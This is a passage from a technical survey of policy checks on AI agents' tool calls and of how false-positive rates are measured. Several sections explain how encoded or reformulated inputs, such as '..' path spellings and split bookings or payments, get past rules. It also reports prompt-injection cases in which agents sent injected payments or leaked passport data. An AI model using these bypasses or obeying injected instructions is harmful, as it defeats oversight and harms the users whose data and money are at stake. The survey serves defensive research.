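Each change fixes one false positive and lets one more harmful command through. Real patterns do not trade errors one for one, and different commands would give different totals. But the owner will probably hear only about the improvements, for the reason Saltzer and Schroeder gave.

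A required form does better on the same commands. This one permits two git commands, a dry run and reading a text file in the current folder:

```
^(git (status|diff|clean -n)|cat [a-z_]+\.txt)$
```

It blocks all four harmful commands and allows two of the three benign ones, so six of its seven verdicts are correct. It blocks the third benign command, the note, and would also block most other commands an agent needs in a day's work. The owner would have to add those one at a time or send unlisted commands to a person.

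### Regular expressions for tool names

JFrog sells a registry that controls which MCP servers a company's agents may use. For each server, an administrator can permit every tool, including any that a later update adds, or write an allowlist or a blocklist of tool names. An entry can be an exact name or a regular expression. JFrog says it uses patterns because MCP tools change often and have no common fixed identifiers.

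JFrog's sample allowlist entry, `^get_.*`, permits `get_user` and `get_logs` and blocks `delete_user`. Its sample blocklist entry, `.*delete.*`, blocks `delete_table`, `user_delete` and `delete_file`. JFrog says that patterns protect a policy against minor tool updates. The allowlist entry would conveniently permit `get_invoice` if an update added it, but it would also permit a new `get_password` tool. The blocklist entry would miss `remove_user` and `drop_table`, and it would block `undelete_file`, which restores a file.

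These lists match only tool names, which the server's developer chooses. A tool called `get_weather` could still send data elsewhere, so patterns are safest on servers whose developers the company trusts. An administrator also can't easily permit every `get_` tool except one, because JFrog offers either an allowlist or a blocklist for each server, and RE2 has no lookaround for writing the exception. Listing the exact names is usually simpler.

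Anchors matter here too. JFrog's samples give the same results whether the registry searches for the pattern anywhere in a tool's name or requires the whole name to match. The entry `get_(user|logs)` gives different results, because a search would also match `forget_user`, which might well be a tool for erasing someone's data.

### Measured error rates

Yang tested AgentTrust's rules on 630 scenarios, mostly from software development. Of these, 188 are labeled safe, 98 moderately risky and 344 dangerous. About 95 hide the command's meaning.

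| Check | Safe actions blocked | Dangerous actions missed |
|---|---|---|
| Blocklist of 50 regular expressions | 0.0% | 85.2% |
| AgentTrust, with 170 rules | 2.1% | 6.4% |

The percentages are consistent with AgentTrust producing 4 false positives among the 188 safe actions and missing 22 of the 344 dangerous ones, and with the blocklist missing 293. The short blocklist had no false positives in this test, but it stopped only about one in seven dangerous actions.

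The 96.7% figure is also probably too favourable, because when a scenario revealed a missing rule, Yang added the rule and kept the scenario in the test. Yang says the result does not show how the system would do on unseen cases. Because AgentTrust rewrites shell text before matching it, the test does not measure regular expressions alone.

Patterns can also raise a benchmark score by matching the test's vocabulary. Yang's other benchmark has 300 scenarios, and some use invented domains such as `evil.com`. Adding four rules for those names raised the share of correct verdicts from 95.0% to 97.0%, although real attackers are unlikely to use such names. Yang keeps these rules out of the normal product and reports 95.0% as the main result.

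## Encoded and reformulated inputs: why they need different remedies

Suppose the office agent has one more tool, `book_room(room, start, days)`, and the office closes on 25 December. The owner adds a rule that blocks any booking whose start date is `2026-12-25`. These two calls both get past it:

```
book_room("A", "25 December 2026", 1)
book_room("A", "2026-12-24", 2)
```

The top call contains an encoded input, which is the forbidden date written in different characters. The check compares it with `2026-12-25`, finds no match and lets the call through, but the booking tool still parses it as 25 December. The bottom call contains a reformulated input. The check and the tool both correctly parse its date as 24 December, but the booking lasts two days, so it also covers the 25th.

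Encoding and reformulation can also get past rules on file paths. `..` means the folder above, so `/office/shared/drafts/../minutes.txt` is another spelling of `/office/shared/minutes.txt`. A rule that compares text may treat them as two files. Reading the minutes with `run_command("cat /office/shared/minutes.txt")` is a reformulation, because a rule on `read_file` doesn't apply to `run_command`.

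To state the difference exactly, write $c(s)$ for the value that the check takes from a text $s$, and $t(s)$ for the value that the tool takes from it. Let $B$ be the set of forbidden values. An encoded input gets through when

$$t(s) \in B \quad\text{but}\quad c(s) \notin B,$$

which can only happen if the check and the tool interpret the text differently. A reformulated input gets through when $c(s) = t(s)$ and the value is not in $B$, but the call has an effect that the rule's author wanted to prevent. Making the check and the tool agree therefore solves the problem of encoding. It does nothing about reformulation, where they agree already.

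### Checking the canonical form

MITRE's *CWE-180* (2006) describes the mistake of checking an input before converting it to canonical form, the single standard spelling of a value. In its example, a program accepts any path that begins with `/safe_dir/` and only then works out where the path leads. A path can begin in that folder and lead out of it again, so the program may approve one location and return another. A different spelling can get past this allowlist because it checks only the start of the text.

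The remedy is a fixed order of steps.

1. Decode the text once, in the way the tool expects. This includes parsing the JSON and undoing any codes that the argument's format uses.
2. Convert each value to canonical form. A date becomes year-month-day, and a path becomes a full path without `..`.
3. Reject whatever is still ambiguous. `04/05/2026` is 4 May in London and 5 April in New York, and no conversion can tell which one the model meant.
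4. Check the canonical value against the rules.
5. Give the tool the value that passed the check, not the original text.

MITRE requires decoding and conversion before the check. It also considers blocklists useful in step 3 for identifying inputs so malformed that the software should reject them outright. Step 3 will block some benign calls, but if the error message gives the required date format (year-month-day), the agent can usually correct the call at once, so each of these false positives causes little disruption.

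Step 5 is easy to overlook. *Oops!... I Parsed It Again* (2026) tested a guard that checked its parsed version of each call but forwarded the original text, and the guard failed in every scenario. MITRE's corrected code returns the canonical path but computes it twice, once to check it and once to return it. Storing and returning the first result would guarantee that the returned path is the one that was checked.

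A person's approval needs the same protection. *The Claws in Plain Sight* (2026) describes a monitor that ties each approval to a digest of the complete call, a short code that changes if any part of the call changes. If the agent alters an argument after the user approves the call, the approval is no longer valid.

Converting paths to canonical form also prevents some false positives. An allowlist with an entry for `/office/shared/minutes.txt` would otherwise block the spelling that goes through `drafts`, although both name the same file.

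The right canonical form depends on the tool. Most Windows computers treat `Minutes.txt` and `minutes.txt` as one file, while most Linux computers treat them as two. If a check on Linux converts every path to lower case, an agent with permission to read one of these files can read both. On Windows, a check that doesn't convert case will miss `minutes.txt` when the rule blocks `Minutes.txt`. It is safest to get the canonical path from the system that will open the file.

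### Why decoding again can go wrong

Decoding a text until nothing changes can remove several layers of encoding, but it can also change the meaning of a text that needed fewer rounds. In a web address, `%25` stands for a percent sign, so a file called `50%.txt` appears as `50%25.txt`. Decoding once gives the right name. If the software decodes it again, it may reject the call or garble the name, because `%.t` is not a valid code. With other names, a second decoding would produce the valid name of a different file.

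Conversion to canonical form doesn't have this problem, because converting a string a second time changes nothing. If $\kappa$ is the conversion, then $\kappa(\kappa(s)) = \kappa(s)$. This isn't true of decoding in general, since a second decoding can change the string again.

A second decoding is most dangerous when it happens after the check, because the tool then acts on a value that was never checked. MITRE's *Double Decoding of the Same Data* notes that decoding an input twice can weaken any protection between the two decodings. GCVE lists a fault of this kind from October 2026 in the web framework Hono. The fault let visitors reach files without the login check running. The developer should therefore find out how many times the tool's input format requires decoding, decode the input exactly that many times before the check, and make sure that nothing decodes it afterwards.

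### Escalating disguised commands

Shell commands mostly lack the convenient canonical forms that dates and paths have, because a command's meaning can depend on variables whose values aren't known until it runs. SecurityWeek's *Decades-Old Bash Tricks Expose AI Coding Agents to Supply Chain Attacks* reports that a 2026 survey found text-based command filters unreliable in ten of eleven open-source agents.

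One response is to ask a person about any command that looks disguised. *CLAWGUARD* (Zhao, Li and colleagues, 2026) describes a policy check with separate blocklists and allowlists for commands, files and network addresses. Calls that match neither list go to the user. Before the check applies its command rules, an obfuscation normaliser scans the text for signs of disguise. The paper's main text says that any such sign sends the command to the user, while its appendix says that only a medium or high score does. Either way, the check doesn't have to work out what the command means.

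The normaliser also simplifies the text before the rules are applied, but the result is not a true canonical form because simplifying can change what a command does. For example, the normaliser deletes quotation marks. `cat "my notes.txt"` reads one file, but without the quotation marks `cat` looks for two, `my` and `notes.txt`. The system could not safely run the simplified text, so the printed algorithm runs the original command with any secrets removed. The rules therefore check different text from what the shell runs, which is presumably one reason to escalate suspicious commands.

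Zhao and colleagues measured how ClawGuard affected agents' success on benign web, operating-system and coding tasks, using five models. The figures below are shares of the same agent's success without ClawGuard.

| Benign tasks | User rejects every request | User grants up to three per task |
|---|---|---|
| Web | 78.5% | 91.7% |
| Operating system | 88.8% | 94.9% |
| Coding | 94.9% | 98.8% |
| Average | 87.4% | 95.1% |

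These figures cover the whole system, so they don't show how many benign commands the normaliser escalated. It probably escalated at least one, since some of the patterns it looks for are ordinary features of shell scripts.

It would also be a mistake to combine the 95.1% with ClawGuard's security results, because Zhao and colleagues denied every request for approval in the attack tests. Under that policy, the share of malicious skill file attacks that failed rose from 56.7% to 86.7%, averaged over the five models. The matching loss in completed tasks is in the left-hand column of figures. When the user grants requests, the agent completes more tasks, but some of those requests may come from an attacker, and the paper doesn't measure how often.

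### Why canonical form cannot cure reformulation

The date in `book_room("A", "2026-12-24", 2)` is already in canonical form, so converting it again changes nothing. To catch this call, the rule has to look at the effect, which is the set of days that the booking covers. It should block the call when

$$\text{start} \le \text{25 December} < \text{start} + \text{days}.$$

That is easy for a single booking tool but much harder for a shell. Chen and Lin found that, even with perfect matching, 69.0% to 98.6% of the shell blocklists that cover a file operation leave another way to perform it.

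One alternative is to replace the free-form command with narrow, typed tools. If the office agent uses the shell only to move old minutes into an archive, its owner could replace `run_command` with `archive_file(name)`. The owner can then check whether each remaining tool could delete a file or book a room, a check nobody could make for every program on a computer. The disadvantage is that the agent can then do only what the tools provide for. As with tool lists, tasks that fail for this reason won't appear in a log of blocked calls.

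Another remedy is to use permissions or a sandbox to limit what a command can do. Hundreds of commands can print a file, but they all have to open it through the operating system. If the agent's account has no permission to read the payroll file, they all fail. Encoding matters less here too, because the operating system checks permissions on the file being opened, however the command spelled the path.

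But permissions are coarse. If the agent needs the payroll file for one legitimate task, the operating system will also let it read the file on an attacker's instructions. And a sandbox that allows connections to the mail server doesn't normally check who an email is going to.

### Combining code analysis with sandboxes

A tool can also have effects that its description doesn't mention. *Towards Practically-Secure Tools for AI Agents* (Adam, Lu and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a `write_file` tool that writes the file as described but also sends usage statistics over the network. No rule on the path or the content would reveal this.

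1. A program analyses the tool's source code and lists every kind of effect the tool could have, such as writing files or using the network.
2. The tool's developer puts a small sandbox around each operation that has an effect. The sandbox receives its limits separately for each call.
3. The program analyses the code again to confirm that no effect lacks a sandbox and that nothing in the tool can alter the limits.
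4. On the user's side, a policy engine blocks the call if the tool has an unprotected effect that the policy forbids. Otherwise, it sends the call with its limits, for example that the tool may write only inside `~/workspace`.

The sandbox checks the actual path when the program tries to write to it. Code analysis runs earlier and has to account for every possible path, so Adam and colleagues warn that analysis alone will reject harmless calls. A tool that could write anywhere looks dangerous even if a given call writes to the right folder.

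The tests covered three scenarios. In each, the system should allow the intended version and block a version with an unwanted effect.

| Protection | Intended versions allowed | Unwanted versions blocked |
|---|---|---|
| None | 3 of 3 | 0 of 3 |
| One fixed sandbox around all the tools | 2 of 3 | 1 of 3 |
| Code analysis alone | 2 of 3 | 3 of 3 |
| Code analysis with a sandbox for each effect | 3 of 3 | 3 of 3 |

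This is a demonstration more than a measurement, because Adam and colleagues chose the six cases themselves, replayed recorded sessions, and assumed that something else had already supplied the correct policy for each call. The prototype handles only tools written in Rust. Adam and colleagues expect more false rejections with Python and JavaScript, which are harder to analyse and widely used by tool developers. The network limits work by site, so they can't distinguish reading a post from publishing one on the same site, and a cautious policy would have to block both.

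### Checking where a value came from

Rules can also depend on a value's provenance, meaning where it came from. *NOMOS* turns a written policy into such rules. For AgentDojo's banking tasks it produced three:

- The agent may send money only to a recipient whom the user named or who already appears in the account's transaction history.
- A new password must come from the user's own messages.
- The agent may change something only if the user asked for a change.

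The check takes its facts from the user's messages and from tool results, never from the agent's own claims. An injected claim that the user has approved a payment therefore has no effect on the verdict. The first rule checks only the recipient, so it also doesn't matter how an attacker words or disguises the payment's description.

*NOMOS* argues that this works because attacks that look varied share a few structural properties. Of the nine attack goals in the banking tasks, seven depend on who receives the money, one depends on who supplied a password, and one is a change that the user did not request. Let $\pi(x)$ be the set of properties that the check can test and that a call must have to achieve attack $x$. If $\pi(x) = \pi(x')$, one rule can block both attacks, so the number of rules depends on the number of different sets, not the number of attacks.

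The argument is sound but limited, because it holds for any list of properties, good or bad. To be useful, the properties must also separate attacks from legitimate calls. If an attack needs only a payment to a known supplier, $\pi(x)$ may contain nothing that distinguishes it from a legitimate payment, and adding rules from the same vocabulary won't help. The researchers also wrote the policies for these tests, because AgentDojo doesn't supply any.

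The banking tests paired user tasks with attack goals in 432 runs. In 183 of them, the agent attempted a call containing the attacker's account or password, and the check blocked every one. In the other 249, the agent never attempted the attacker's call, so those runs provide little evidence about the rules. Without the rules, 46.5% of the standard attacks succeeded.

The harmful calls that the rules admitted are informative too:

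- In 8 of the 288 runs with the standard attack, and 7 of the 144 with an adaptive one, the agent sent an injected payment to somebody already in the transaction history. With a second model, Llama 3.3 70B, this happened in 11 of 140 runs and moved $41,250. Most of that was a total split into four payments, which a cumulative limit could have stopped.
- In a travel task, the agent created a calendar event that an injection had asked for. The written policy required the user to have requested the event, but the compiled rule only required the user to have requested some change, and this user had asked for an email.
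- Also in the travel tasks, the second model emailed the user's passport and card numbers to an address that the user had named. The recipient's provenance was fine, but the rule did not cover the contents.
- In an office task, the check refused to delete file 11, as the user had asked. The agent then deleted file 1, and the check allowed it because the user's message contained a "1" as a list number.

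The last case is a failure of interpretation, much like those caused by encoded inputs, although nobody had disguised anything. Applying a provenance rule still requires determining whether two texts refer to the same thing.

### When the user doesn't name the target

The cost to benign work varied enormously between AgentDojo's four groups of tasks.

| Tasks | Attacks that succeeded, without and with rules | Benign tasks completed, without and with rules |
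|---|---|---|
| Travel | 10.0%, 3.6% | 75.0%, 70.0% |
| Banking | 46.5%, 0.0% | 79.2%, 70.8% |
| Workspace | 7.3%, 0.0% | 87.5%, 65.0% |
| Slack | 70.5%, 0.0% | 90.5%, 14.3% |

The losses on travel and banking could be due to chance, but those on workspace and Slack are too large. Slack tasks often require the agent to act on something it reads, such as a link in a colleague's message. An attacker's link also arrives in a message, so a rule that permits only links the user named blocks both, and the agent then completes about one benign task in seven.

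The same thing happens on a smaller scale in banking. If the user asks the agent to pay a bill and the account number appears only in the bill, the rule blocks a legitimate payment. Accepting account numbers from bills would let that payment through, but it would also allow payments to any account that an attacker writes into a bill.

*NOMOS* also ran Progent on the banking tasks with the same model. Progent let 5.6% of attacks succeed, mostly in tasks such as "pay the bill, like last month", where the request doesn't name an account, so an LLM has no basis for writing a recipient rule. The transaction history supplies some of the missing information, but it then needs protection too, because a false entry would make its recipient acceptable. AgentDojo's attacks can't create new entries, so the tests don't cover this risk.

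Other systems track where each value came from. In Agent-Sentry, the model declares an argument's source, and Sequeira and colleagues treat the value as unverifiable if that source doesn't contain it. The monitor in *The Claws in Plain Sight* extends the idea to values that software derives from protected data. It can block a marketing call that contains a category computed from someone's income, which a search for the income figure itself would miss.

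### How the four types of rule compare

The table applies when the check receives the call's values as the model wrote them, apart from ordinary parsing. Regex constraints have two rows because a required form and a forbidden pattern fail differently.

| Rule | Encoded input | Reformulated input |
|---|---|---|
| Blocklist | Weak: a spelling that is not on the list passes | Weak: any unlisted call with the same effect passes |
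| Allowlist | Strong if it compares whole values, because an unfamiliar spelling matches no entry; weaker if it compares only the start of a text | Strong against tools and values left off the list; weak if a permitted tool can do many things |
| Range constraint | Strong for typed numbers, which keep the same value in any spelling; weak for dates and amounts that remain text | Weak: several calls can each stay within the bound and together exceed it |
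| Regex constraint, required form | Strong if the pattern is narrow and anchored, because most other spellings don't fit it | Weak if the pattern is broad, because every value of the right form passes, whatever its effect |
| Regex constraint, forbidden pattern | Weak: the same value in other characters may not contain the pattern | Weak: another call with the same effect need not contain the pattern |

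Allowlists and required forms are strong against encoded input because they block unfamiliar spellings, but they also block benign calls that use those spellings. Converting values to canonical form before checking them lets more of those benign calls through and helps blocklists and forbidden patterns catch more harmful ones, but it makes no difference for reformulated input.

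## What counts as a false positive

The false-positive rate is the share of benign, authorised calls that the check blocks. The measured rate depends on the unit counted, the firm's authorisation rules and the calls included in the test. Suppose an office agent makes 40 benign calls over ten tasks in one session, and the check blocks three of them, all attempts to send the same email to Carla, a new client. If the emails were authorised, the rate is 3 in 40 by call, 1 in 10 by task and 1 in 1 by session. If the firm requires a manager to approve new contacts and nobody has approved Carla, the emails were unauthorised and the rate is zero. The rate is also zero if the test leaves out emails to Carla.

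A published false-positive rate means little unless readers know whether it counts calls, tasks or sessions, who decided which calls were authorised, and what benign set it was measured on.

### Blocked and wrongly blocked

An agent with a legitimate task can still make unauthorised calls. Running an agent on benign tasks and counting every block is the easiest way to look for false positives, but the count also includes any blocks that correctly stopped those calls.

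*TACT-Bench* (Hashemi Rad, Wu et al., 2026) simulates a shop where an agent handles returns, refunds and account changes under a written policy, and a model plays the customer. It tests two checks on tool calls that change something. Tool-Guard applies fixed rules, handwritten from the policy, to the call's arguments, the shop's database and the results of earlier lookups. Policy-Guard, adapted from the PolicyGuard system that *NOMOS* reimplemented, asks an LLM to judge the call, and the LLM also reads the policy, the conversation and a checklist for the tool. Each check ran on 1,242 benign conversations.

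| | Tool-Guard (fixed rules) | Policy-Guard (LLM) |
|---|---|---|
| Benign conversations with at least one block | 32 (2.6%) | 307 (24.7%) |
| Blocked calls that were unauthorised | 32 | 52 |
| Blocked calls that were authorised and passed later | 0 | 175 |
| Blocked calls that were authorised and never passed | 0 | 147 |

None of Tool-Guard's 32 blocks on benign tasks was a false positive. The customers' requests were legitimate, but the agent tried to meet them in ways the policy forbids, for example by settling a valid refund with store credit that nobody had approved. Six models played the agent, and all 32 blocks occurred with the three open-weight ones. With Tool-Guard, the agents completed 95.6% of benign tasks on average, up from 92.7% without it. Treating every block on a benign task as a false positive would count these corrections as errors.

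Policy-Guard produced false positives: it never let through 147 authorised calls. These fell in 101 conversations, or 8.1% of the total, and the agent failed the task in 100 of them. In one of those failures, the shop had already approved a refund without a return. The agent found the approval, read the details back to the customer, got a clear yes and requested the refund. Policy-Guard blocked the request three times because it required separate proof that somebody had reviewed the claim, although under the policy the approval itself was that proof. The agent gave up and passed the customer to a person.

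The 175 calls that passed later are harder to classify. Policy-Guard first blocked them pending a step such as getting the customer's explicit confirmation. If the agent had skipped a required step, the call was not yet authorised and the block was right, but if the agent had already completed it, the block was a false positive that added an extra turn. The published counts don't separate these cases. Policy-Guard checked 1,318 calls in the benign conversations, and its false-positive rate per call is about 12% if none of the 175 blocks were mistakes and about 25% if all of them were. Both figures exclude the 52 unauthorised calls it blocked and assume that every call it passed was authorised.

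The number of blocks can also mislead when you compare two versions of the same check. Hashemi Rad and colleagues retested Policy-Guard without its checklist, with Claude Opus 4.8 as the agent. The number of benign conversations with a block fell from 32 to 10, but the number in which an authorised call never passed fell only from 17 to 9, so the checklist had caused many blocks that were harmless or correct.

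Tool-Guard's perfect score is less impressive than it looks, because before the experiment the researchers replayed the benchmark's own authorised calls through the rules and confirmed that none were blocked. This check is good practice for anyone deploying fixed rules, but it makes false positives on those tasks very unlikely and provides little evidence about requests outside the benchmark. The benchmark leaves out many requests, since its 1,242 conversations come from only 23 tasks. Each task has nine copies that differ in details such as names and order numbers, and six models ran every copy.

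The labels depend on the researchers' list of authorised calls for each task. If the check blocked an acceptable solution that was not on the list, the block would count as correct. This could affect at most one of Tool-Guard's blocks and 31 of Policy-Guard's, since the other unauthorised calls used tools that the task explicitly forbids.

The fixed rules avoided false positives while still preventing some violations. In conversations where the customer was trying to manipulate the agent, the share with a forbidden call or an unauthorised change fell from 17.3% with no check to 8.4% with Tool-Guard's fixed rules and 6.6% with Policy-Guard, which uses an LLM. The shop could therefore have had most of that reduction without the LLM and its false positives.

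### Calls that nobody can label

Some calls can't be labelled from their name and arguments alone. The command `git push origin main` is ordinary work if `origin` is the project's own repository, but it could leak the code if `origin` belongs to somebody else.

Beno tested policy gates on 2,643 synthetic tool calls, grouped around 106 scenarios. Each group includes hazardous calls, hard negatives, calls whose label needs more evidence, and calls containing text written to instruct the model. GPT-6 wrote the calls and labelled them against a set of rules. Claude Opus 5.5 labelled them again without seeing the first labels, and the two models agreed on 99.9% of individual labels and on every label for 96.6% of calls. This agreement is good evidence that the written labelling instructions were clear, but weaker evidence that the labels match what a user would want, because no user took part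 in the comparison.

The test allows a label of "unknown" and leaves those labels out of the results, which is more honest than guessing but excludes some of the hardest decisions. Of the 1,108 calls that Beno reserved for the final test, 768 broke at least one of the 23 rules scored and 252 clearly broke none. For the remaining 88, no label showed a violation, but at least one label was missing.

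Jev 1.14, a model that returns a probability for each rule instead of text, wrongly interrupted 12 of the 252 clean calls, or 4.8%, in its better configuration. Counting all 88 unsettled calls as benign would make the rate 3.5% if Jev interrupted none of them and 29% if it interrupted them all. Neither extreme is likely. But a deployed gate has to decide on such calls, so an evaluation should at least report how many the gate interrupts.

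### Which benign calls are in the test

*NetInjectBench* (Shayoni, Shoaib and colleagues, 2026) includes a defence that shows how much the choice of benign calls can matter. The paper's simulated agent helps run a computer network using six tools, for tasks such as fetching logs, opening a ticket or applying a configuration change. The defence, called a "static allowlist", disables `apply_config_change` and permits the other five tools. Because the set of tools is fixed, this is the same policy as a blocklist with one entry.

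Three small models each ran 40 routine scenarios and 10 in which the right action was an already approved configuration change. The list blocked all 30 approved changes and nothing in the 120 routine runs, because only the approved changes required the disabled tool. The false-positive rate is 0% if you count only the routine runs, 100% if you count only the approved changes, and 20% if you count all 150 runs.

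In general, if a share $w_k$ of benign calls is of kind $k$, and the check wrongly blocks a share $r_k$ of that kind, the overall rate is

$$r = \sum_k w_k r_k.$$

For the disabled tool, $r_k$ is 1 for approved changes and 0 for routine work, so the overall rate equals the share of approved changes. That share is 20% in the benchmark because Shayoni and colleagues wrote 40 routine scenarios and ten approved changes. If approved changes were 1% of an agent's real work, the rate would be 1%, although the agent still couldn't apply any of them. An evaluation should therefore give the rate for each kind of call, so that readers can use their own weights and can see if there is a job the agent can never do, even when the average is low.

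Shayoni and colleagues also tested a gate that checks each configuration change against a trusted record of approved changes, including the device and time for each. It allowed all 30 approved changes. It also blocked two proposals in the 120 routine runs, but these were probably not false positives. The models took an unsafe action in two routine runs with no defence and in none with the gate, and the number of runs that ended in a useful action rose from 116 to 118. The researchers distinguish blocks from false positives by reporting a "block rate" for all blocked proposals and an "overblocking rate" for those that were both safe and useful.

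The record was complete and correct in all ten approved scenarios. In a separate test, the gate blocked all 90 mismatches between the call and the record, such as an expired maintenance window or a missing request number. Blocking is right when the mismatch comes from an attack, but in a real company some mismatches would be clerical errors in the record of a legitimate change, and the gate would block those changes too. Its false-positive rate depends on how well the company keeps its records, which the benchmark cannot measure.

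Hard negatives, which are harmless calls that look dangerous, raise the overall false positive rate, whereas easy routine work lowers it. Hard negatives help find rules that are too broad, and Beno's set deliberately includes many of them. Ordinary coding work presumably has fewer, so a rate measured on hard negatives will probably be higher than users experience. Beno built synthetic calls because his users' real ones are private, and he says the interruption rates do not estimate the burden in production. A random sample of an organisation's own calls would give a better estimate, although somebody would have to label them.

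### From one rule to a whole session

A policy check usually applies many rules to each call, and the rate for one rule can be much lower than the rate for the whole policy. If forbid rule $i$ wrongly blocks a share $q_i$ of benign calls, the share $q$ that at least one rule wrongly blocks satisfies

$$\max_i q_i \;\le\; q \;\le\; \sum_i q_i.$$

If twenty block rules each wrongly block 0.2% of benign calls, together they block between 0.2% and 4% of those calls. The total is 4% if no two rules block the same call, and 0.2% if all twenty block the same calls. These bounds hold as long as all the rates come from the same benign set. They do not apply to allow rules, because a new entry on an allowlist can only let more calls through, so it never adds a false positive.

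In Beno's results, the false-positive rate per rule is much lower than the rate of interruptions per action. These rates are for a model rather than for fixed rules, but the same arithmetic applies. With a one-sentence definition of each rule, Jev 1.14 had a false-positive rate of 2.49% per rule and interrupted 77 of the 252 clean calls (30.6%). Adding examples and counterexamples to each definition cut the rate per rule by about two thirds, to 0.83%, and interruptions by more than five sixths, to 4.8%. Beno's company makes a gate of this kind, so he has an interest in good results, but he reports both units and recommends interruptions per action, the less flattering one.

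The false-alarm rate per rule does not reliably predict interruptions across models either. On the same examples, OpenAI's Decisions API and Liquid AI's d1 had similar rates per rule, 1.24% and 1.39%, but interrupted 11.5% and 24.2% of clean calls. One reason is that false alarms may be spread over many calls or concentrated on a few. Another is that the rate per rule includes false alarms on hazardous calls, which don't interrupt clean work. For example, a model may correctly flag a deletion but also wrongly flag it as a production change.

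Tasks consist of many calls, which multiplies the problem again. If each benign call has probability $q$ of a wrongful block, and the errors are independent, the probability of at least one in a task of $m$ calls is

$$1 - (1-q)^m.$$

A check that wrongly blocks 0.5% of benign calls will interrupt about 39% of tasks that make 100 such calls ($1 - 0.995^{100} \approx 0.39$).

| False-positive rate per call | Interrupted tasks of 10 calls | Interrupted tasks of 100 calls | Interrupted sessions of 500 calls |
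|---|---|---|---|
| 0.05% | 0.5% | 4.9% | 22% |
| 0.5% | 4.9% | 39% | 92% |
| 2% | 18% | 87% | over 99.9% |

In practice, false positives are rarely independent. If the recipient list omits Carla, the check will block every email to her in a task about her account and none in most other tasks. At 0.5% per call, a task of 100 calls averages 0.5 false positives. If they always came in groups of ten, they would interrupt only 5% of tasks, not the 39% expected if they were independent. Retries also group false positives, as when Policy-Guard blocked the same refund three times. The formula is therefore best used as a warning that a low rate per call may still interrupt many tasks. Measuring the rate per task requires running whole tasks and counting how many are interrupted by false positives.

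An agent may still complete an interrupted task in another permitted way. A task can also fail without any blocked call, and *Sapien* reports that agents gave up when they saw that a tool was missing. Comparing completion rates with and without the check covers both cases, but it also includes failures unrelated to the rules, so it is worth reporting alongside the false-positive rate, not instead of it.

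### How often a block is right

Suppose an agent makes 10,000 calls, of which 10 are malicious. The check blocks 90% of malicious calls and has a false-positive rate of 1%. It then blocks 9 malicious calls and about 100 of the 9,990 benign ones, so only about 8% of its blocks are correct. If a share $p$ of calls is malicious, the check detects a share $d$ of them and the false-positive rate is $q$, the share of correct blocks is

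$$\frac{p\,d}{p\,d + (1-p)\,q}.$$

Here, the share of blocks that are correct is $0.0009 / (0.0009 + 0.00999)$, or 8.3%. On a benchmark with equal numbers of malicious and benign calls, 99% of the same check's blocks would be correct, because attacks are more common there. A benchmark's share of correct blocks is therefore almost useless for predicting the share in deployment, unless attacks are equally common in both. The false-positive rate and the detection rate transfer to deployment better, provided that the calls are similar.

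For half the blocks to be correct in this example, the false-positive rate would have to fall from 1% to about 0.09%. Even at 1%, the check is probably worth having if each of the nine malicious calls would have sent out the payroll file and most of the hundred benign ones need only a small correction. But anyone who reads the log of blocked calls will find about eleven harmless calls for every attack, and may well stop reading it.

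### Restrictions, hand-offs and prompts

Many systems have outcomes between allowing and blocking, and the false-positive rate depends on how the evaluator counts them. In *ToolGuardian*, for example, the policy can reject a tool, admit it with restrictions, admit it with a warning or simply admit it, and the scoring counts only rejection as a block. Part of that evaluation concerns vetting tools before an agent may use them rather than checking calls.

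The test included eight benign tools. With evidence from the tools' descriptions, system calls and trial runs, the logic-based version of the policy restricted all eight and rejected none. The paper counts only rejections as false positives, so the rate was 0%, but it would be 100% if restrictions also counted. When the researchers added source-code analysis, the policy rejected two of the tools and restricted the other six. That raised the rate to 25% by the paper's scoring, and it would still be 100% with restrictions included.

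The same choice affects the malicious tools. Before the source-code analysis, the policy rejected six of the eight and restricted the other two, which the scoring counts as misses. Counting restrictions as blocks would make those two successes, but it would also mean the policy blocked all sixteen tools, including the benign ones. *ToolGuardian* reports the restrictions separately and calls them operational friction. The amount of friction depends on what the restriction prevents. For example, losing network access would disrupt a weather service but not a calculator. Only a test on real tasks could show which case is more common.

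*TACT-Bench* is much stricter. If the agent hands a benign task to a person, the task counts as a failure with no partial credit, even if the final state of the database is correct. Both choices are defensible, but two rates can't sensibly be compared if one counts partial interventions as successes and the other counts them as failures. Reporting separate rates for blocked and escalated calls is safer.

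A block can also lead an agent to hand a conversation over to staff without an instruction from the check to do so. In a longer version of the shop test, the customer makes a legitimate request first and attempts the attack afterwards. Claude Opus 4.8 handed over one conversation before completing the legitimate request when there was no check, and 19 of 353 with Policy-Guard. GPT-5.6 Sol handed over two with no check and 29 of 353 with Policy-Guard. Hashemi Rad and colleagues leave these conversations out of the attack results because the attack never began, but the shop's staff would still have to deal with them.

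Escalating a call to the user instead of blocking it turns a false positive into a delay. If the check in the base-rate example asked the user about each of its 109 suspicious calls, and each answer took ten seconds, the user would spend about 18 minutes answering over 10,000 calls. The delay to the task can be much longer, because the agent may have to wait for the user to respond. A task that starts in the evening may stop at the first prompt and make no progress until morning.

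The larger worry is approval fatigue, but we can't tell from Anthropic's 93% approval rate, which Chen and Lin cited, whether users catch attacks. In this example, a careful user would approve the 100 benign calls and refuse the nine malicious ones, for an approval rate of 92%. A user who approved 93% of requests at random would have almost the same rate but let through about eight of the nine malicious calls.

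The 93% approval rate gives a rough idea of how often prompts interrupt users unnecessarily. If those approvals were correct, more than nine in ten prompts were for calls that could have run without asking. That makes fatigue plausible, because a user who sees about thirteen acceptable requests for each one worth refusing has little reason to keep reading carefully. Measuring whether people answer faster and approve more as a session goes on would give better evidence. The most direct test would be to plant harmless imitations of harmful requests among the real ones and count how many of them users approve.

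## Confidence intervals for false-positive rates

*Parallax* reports a test on 50 legitimate development actions, in which the system's default configuration blocked none and its maximum-security configuration blocked 18. The paper claims "zero false positives" for the default, which is true of those 50 actions, but a prospective user needs the rate for the thousands of calls their own agent will make. A system that wrongly blocks one call in fifty still has a 36% chance of blocking none of 50 legitimate calls ($0.98^{50} \approx 0.36$).

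A confidence interval shows how precisely a sample of a given size estimates a check's false-positive rate. If 100 firms each tested the same check on their own random sample of benign calls from the same source and computed a 95% interval, about 95 of the intervals would contain the true rate. The 95% describes how often the method succeeds over many samples. Bowyer, Aitchison and Ivanova (2025), in *Don't Use the CLT in LLM Evals*, point out that people often misread it as the probability that the true rate lies in one particular interval.

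### Why the textbook interval fails near zero

If the check blocks $x$ of $n$ benign calls, the observed rate is $\hat p = x/n$. The textbook interval, also called the normal or Wald interval, is

$$\hat p \pm z\sqrt{\frac{\hat p(1-\hat p)}{n}},$$

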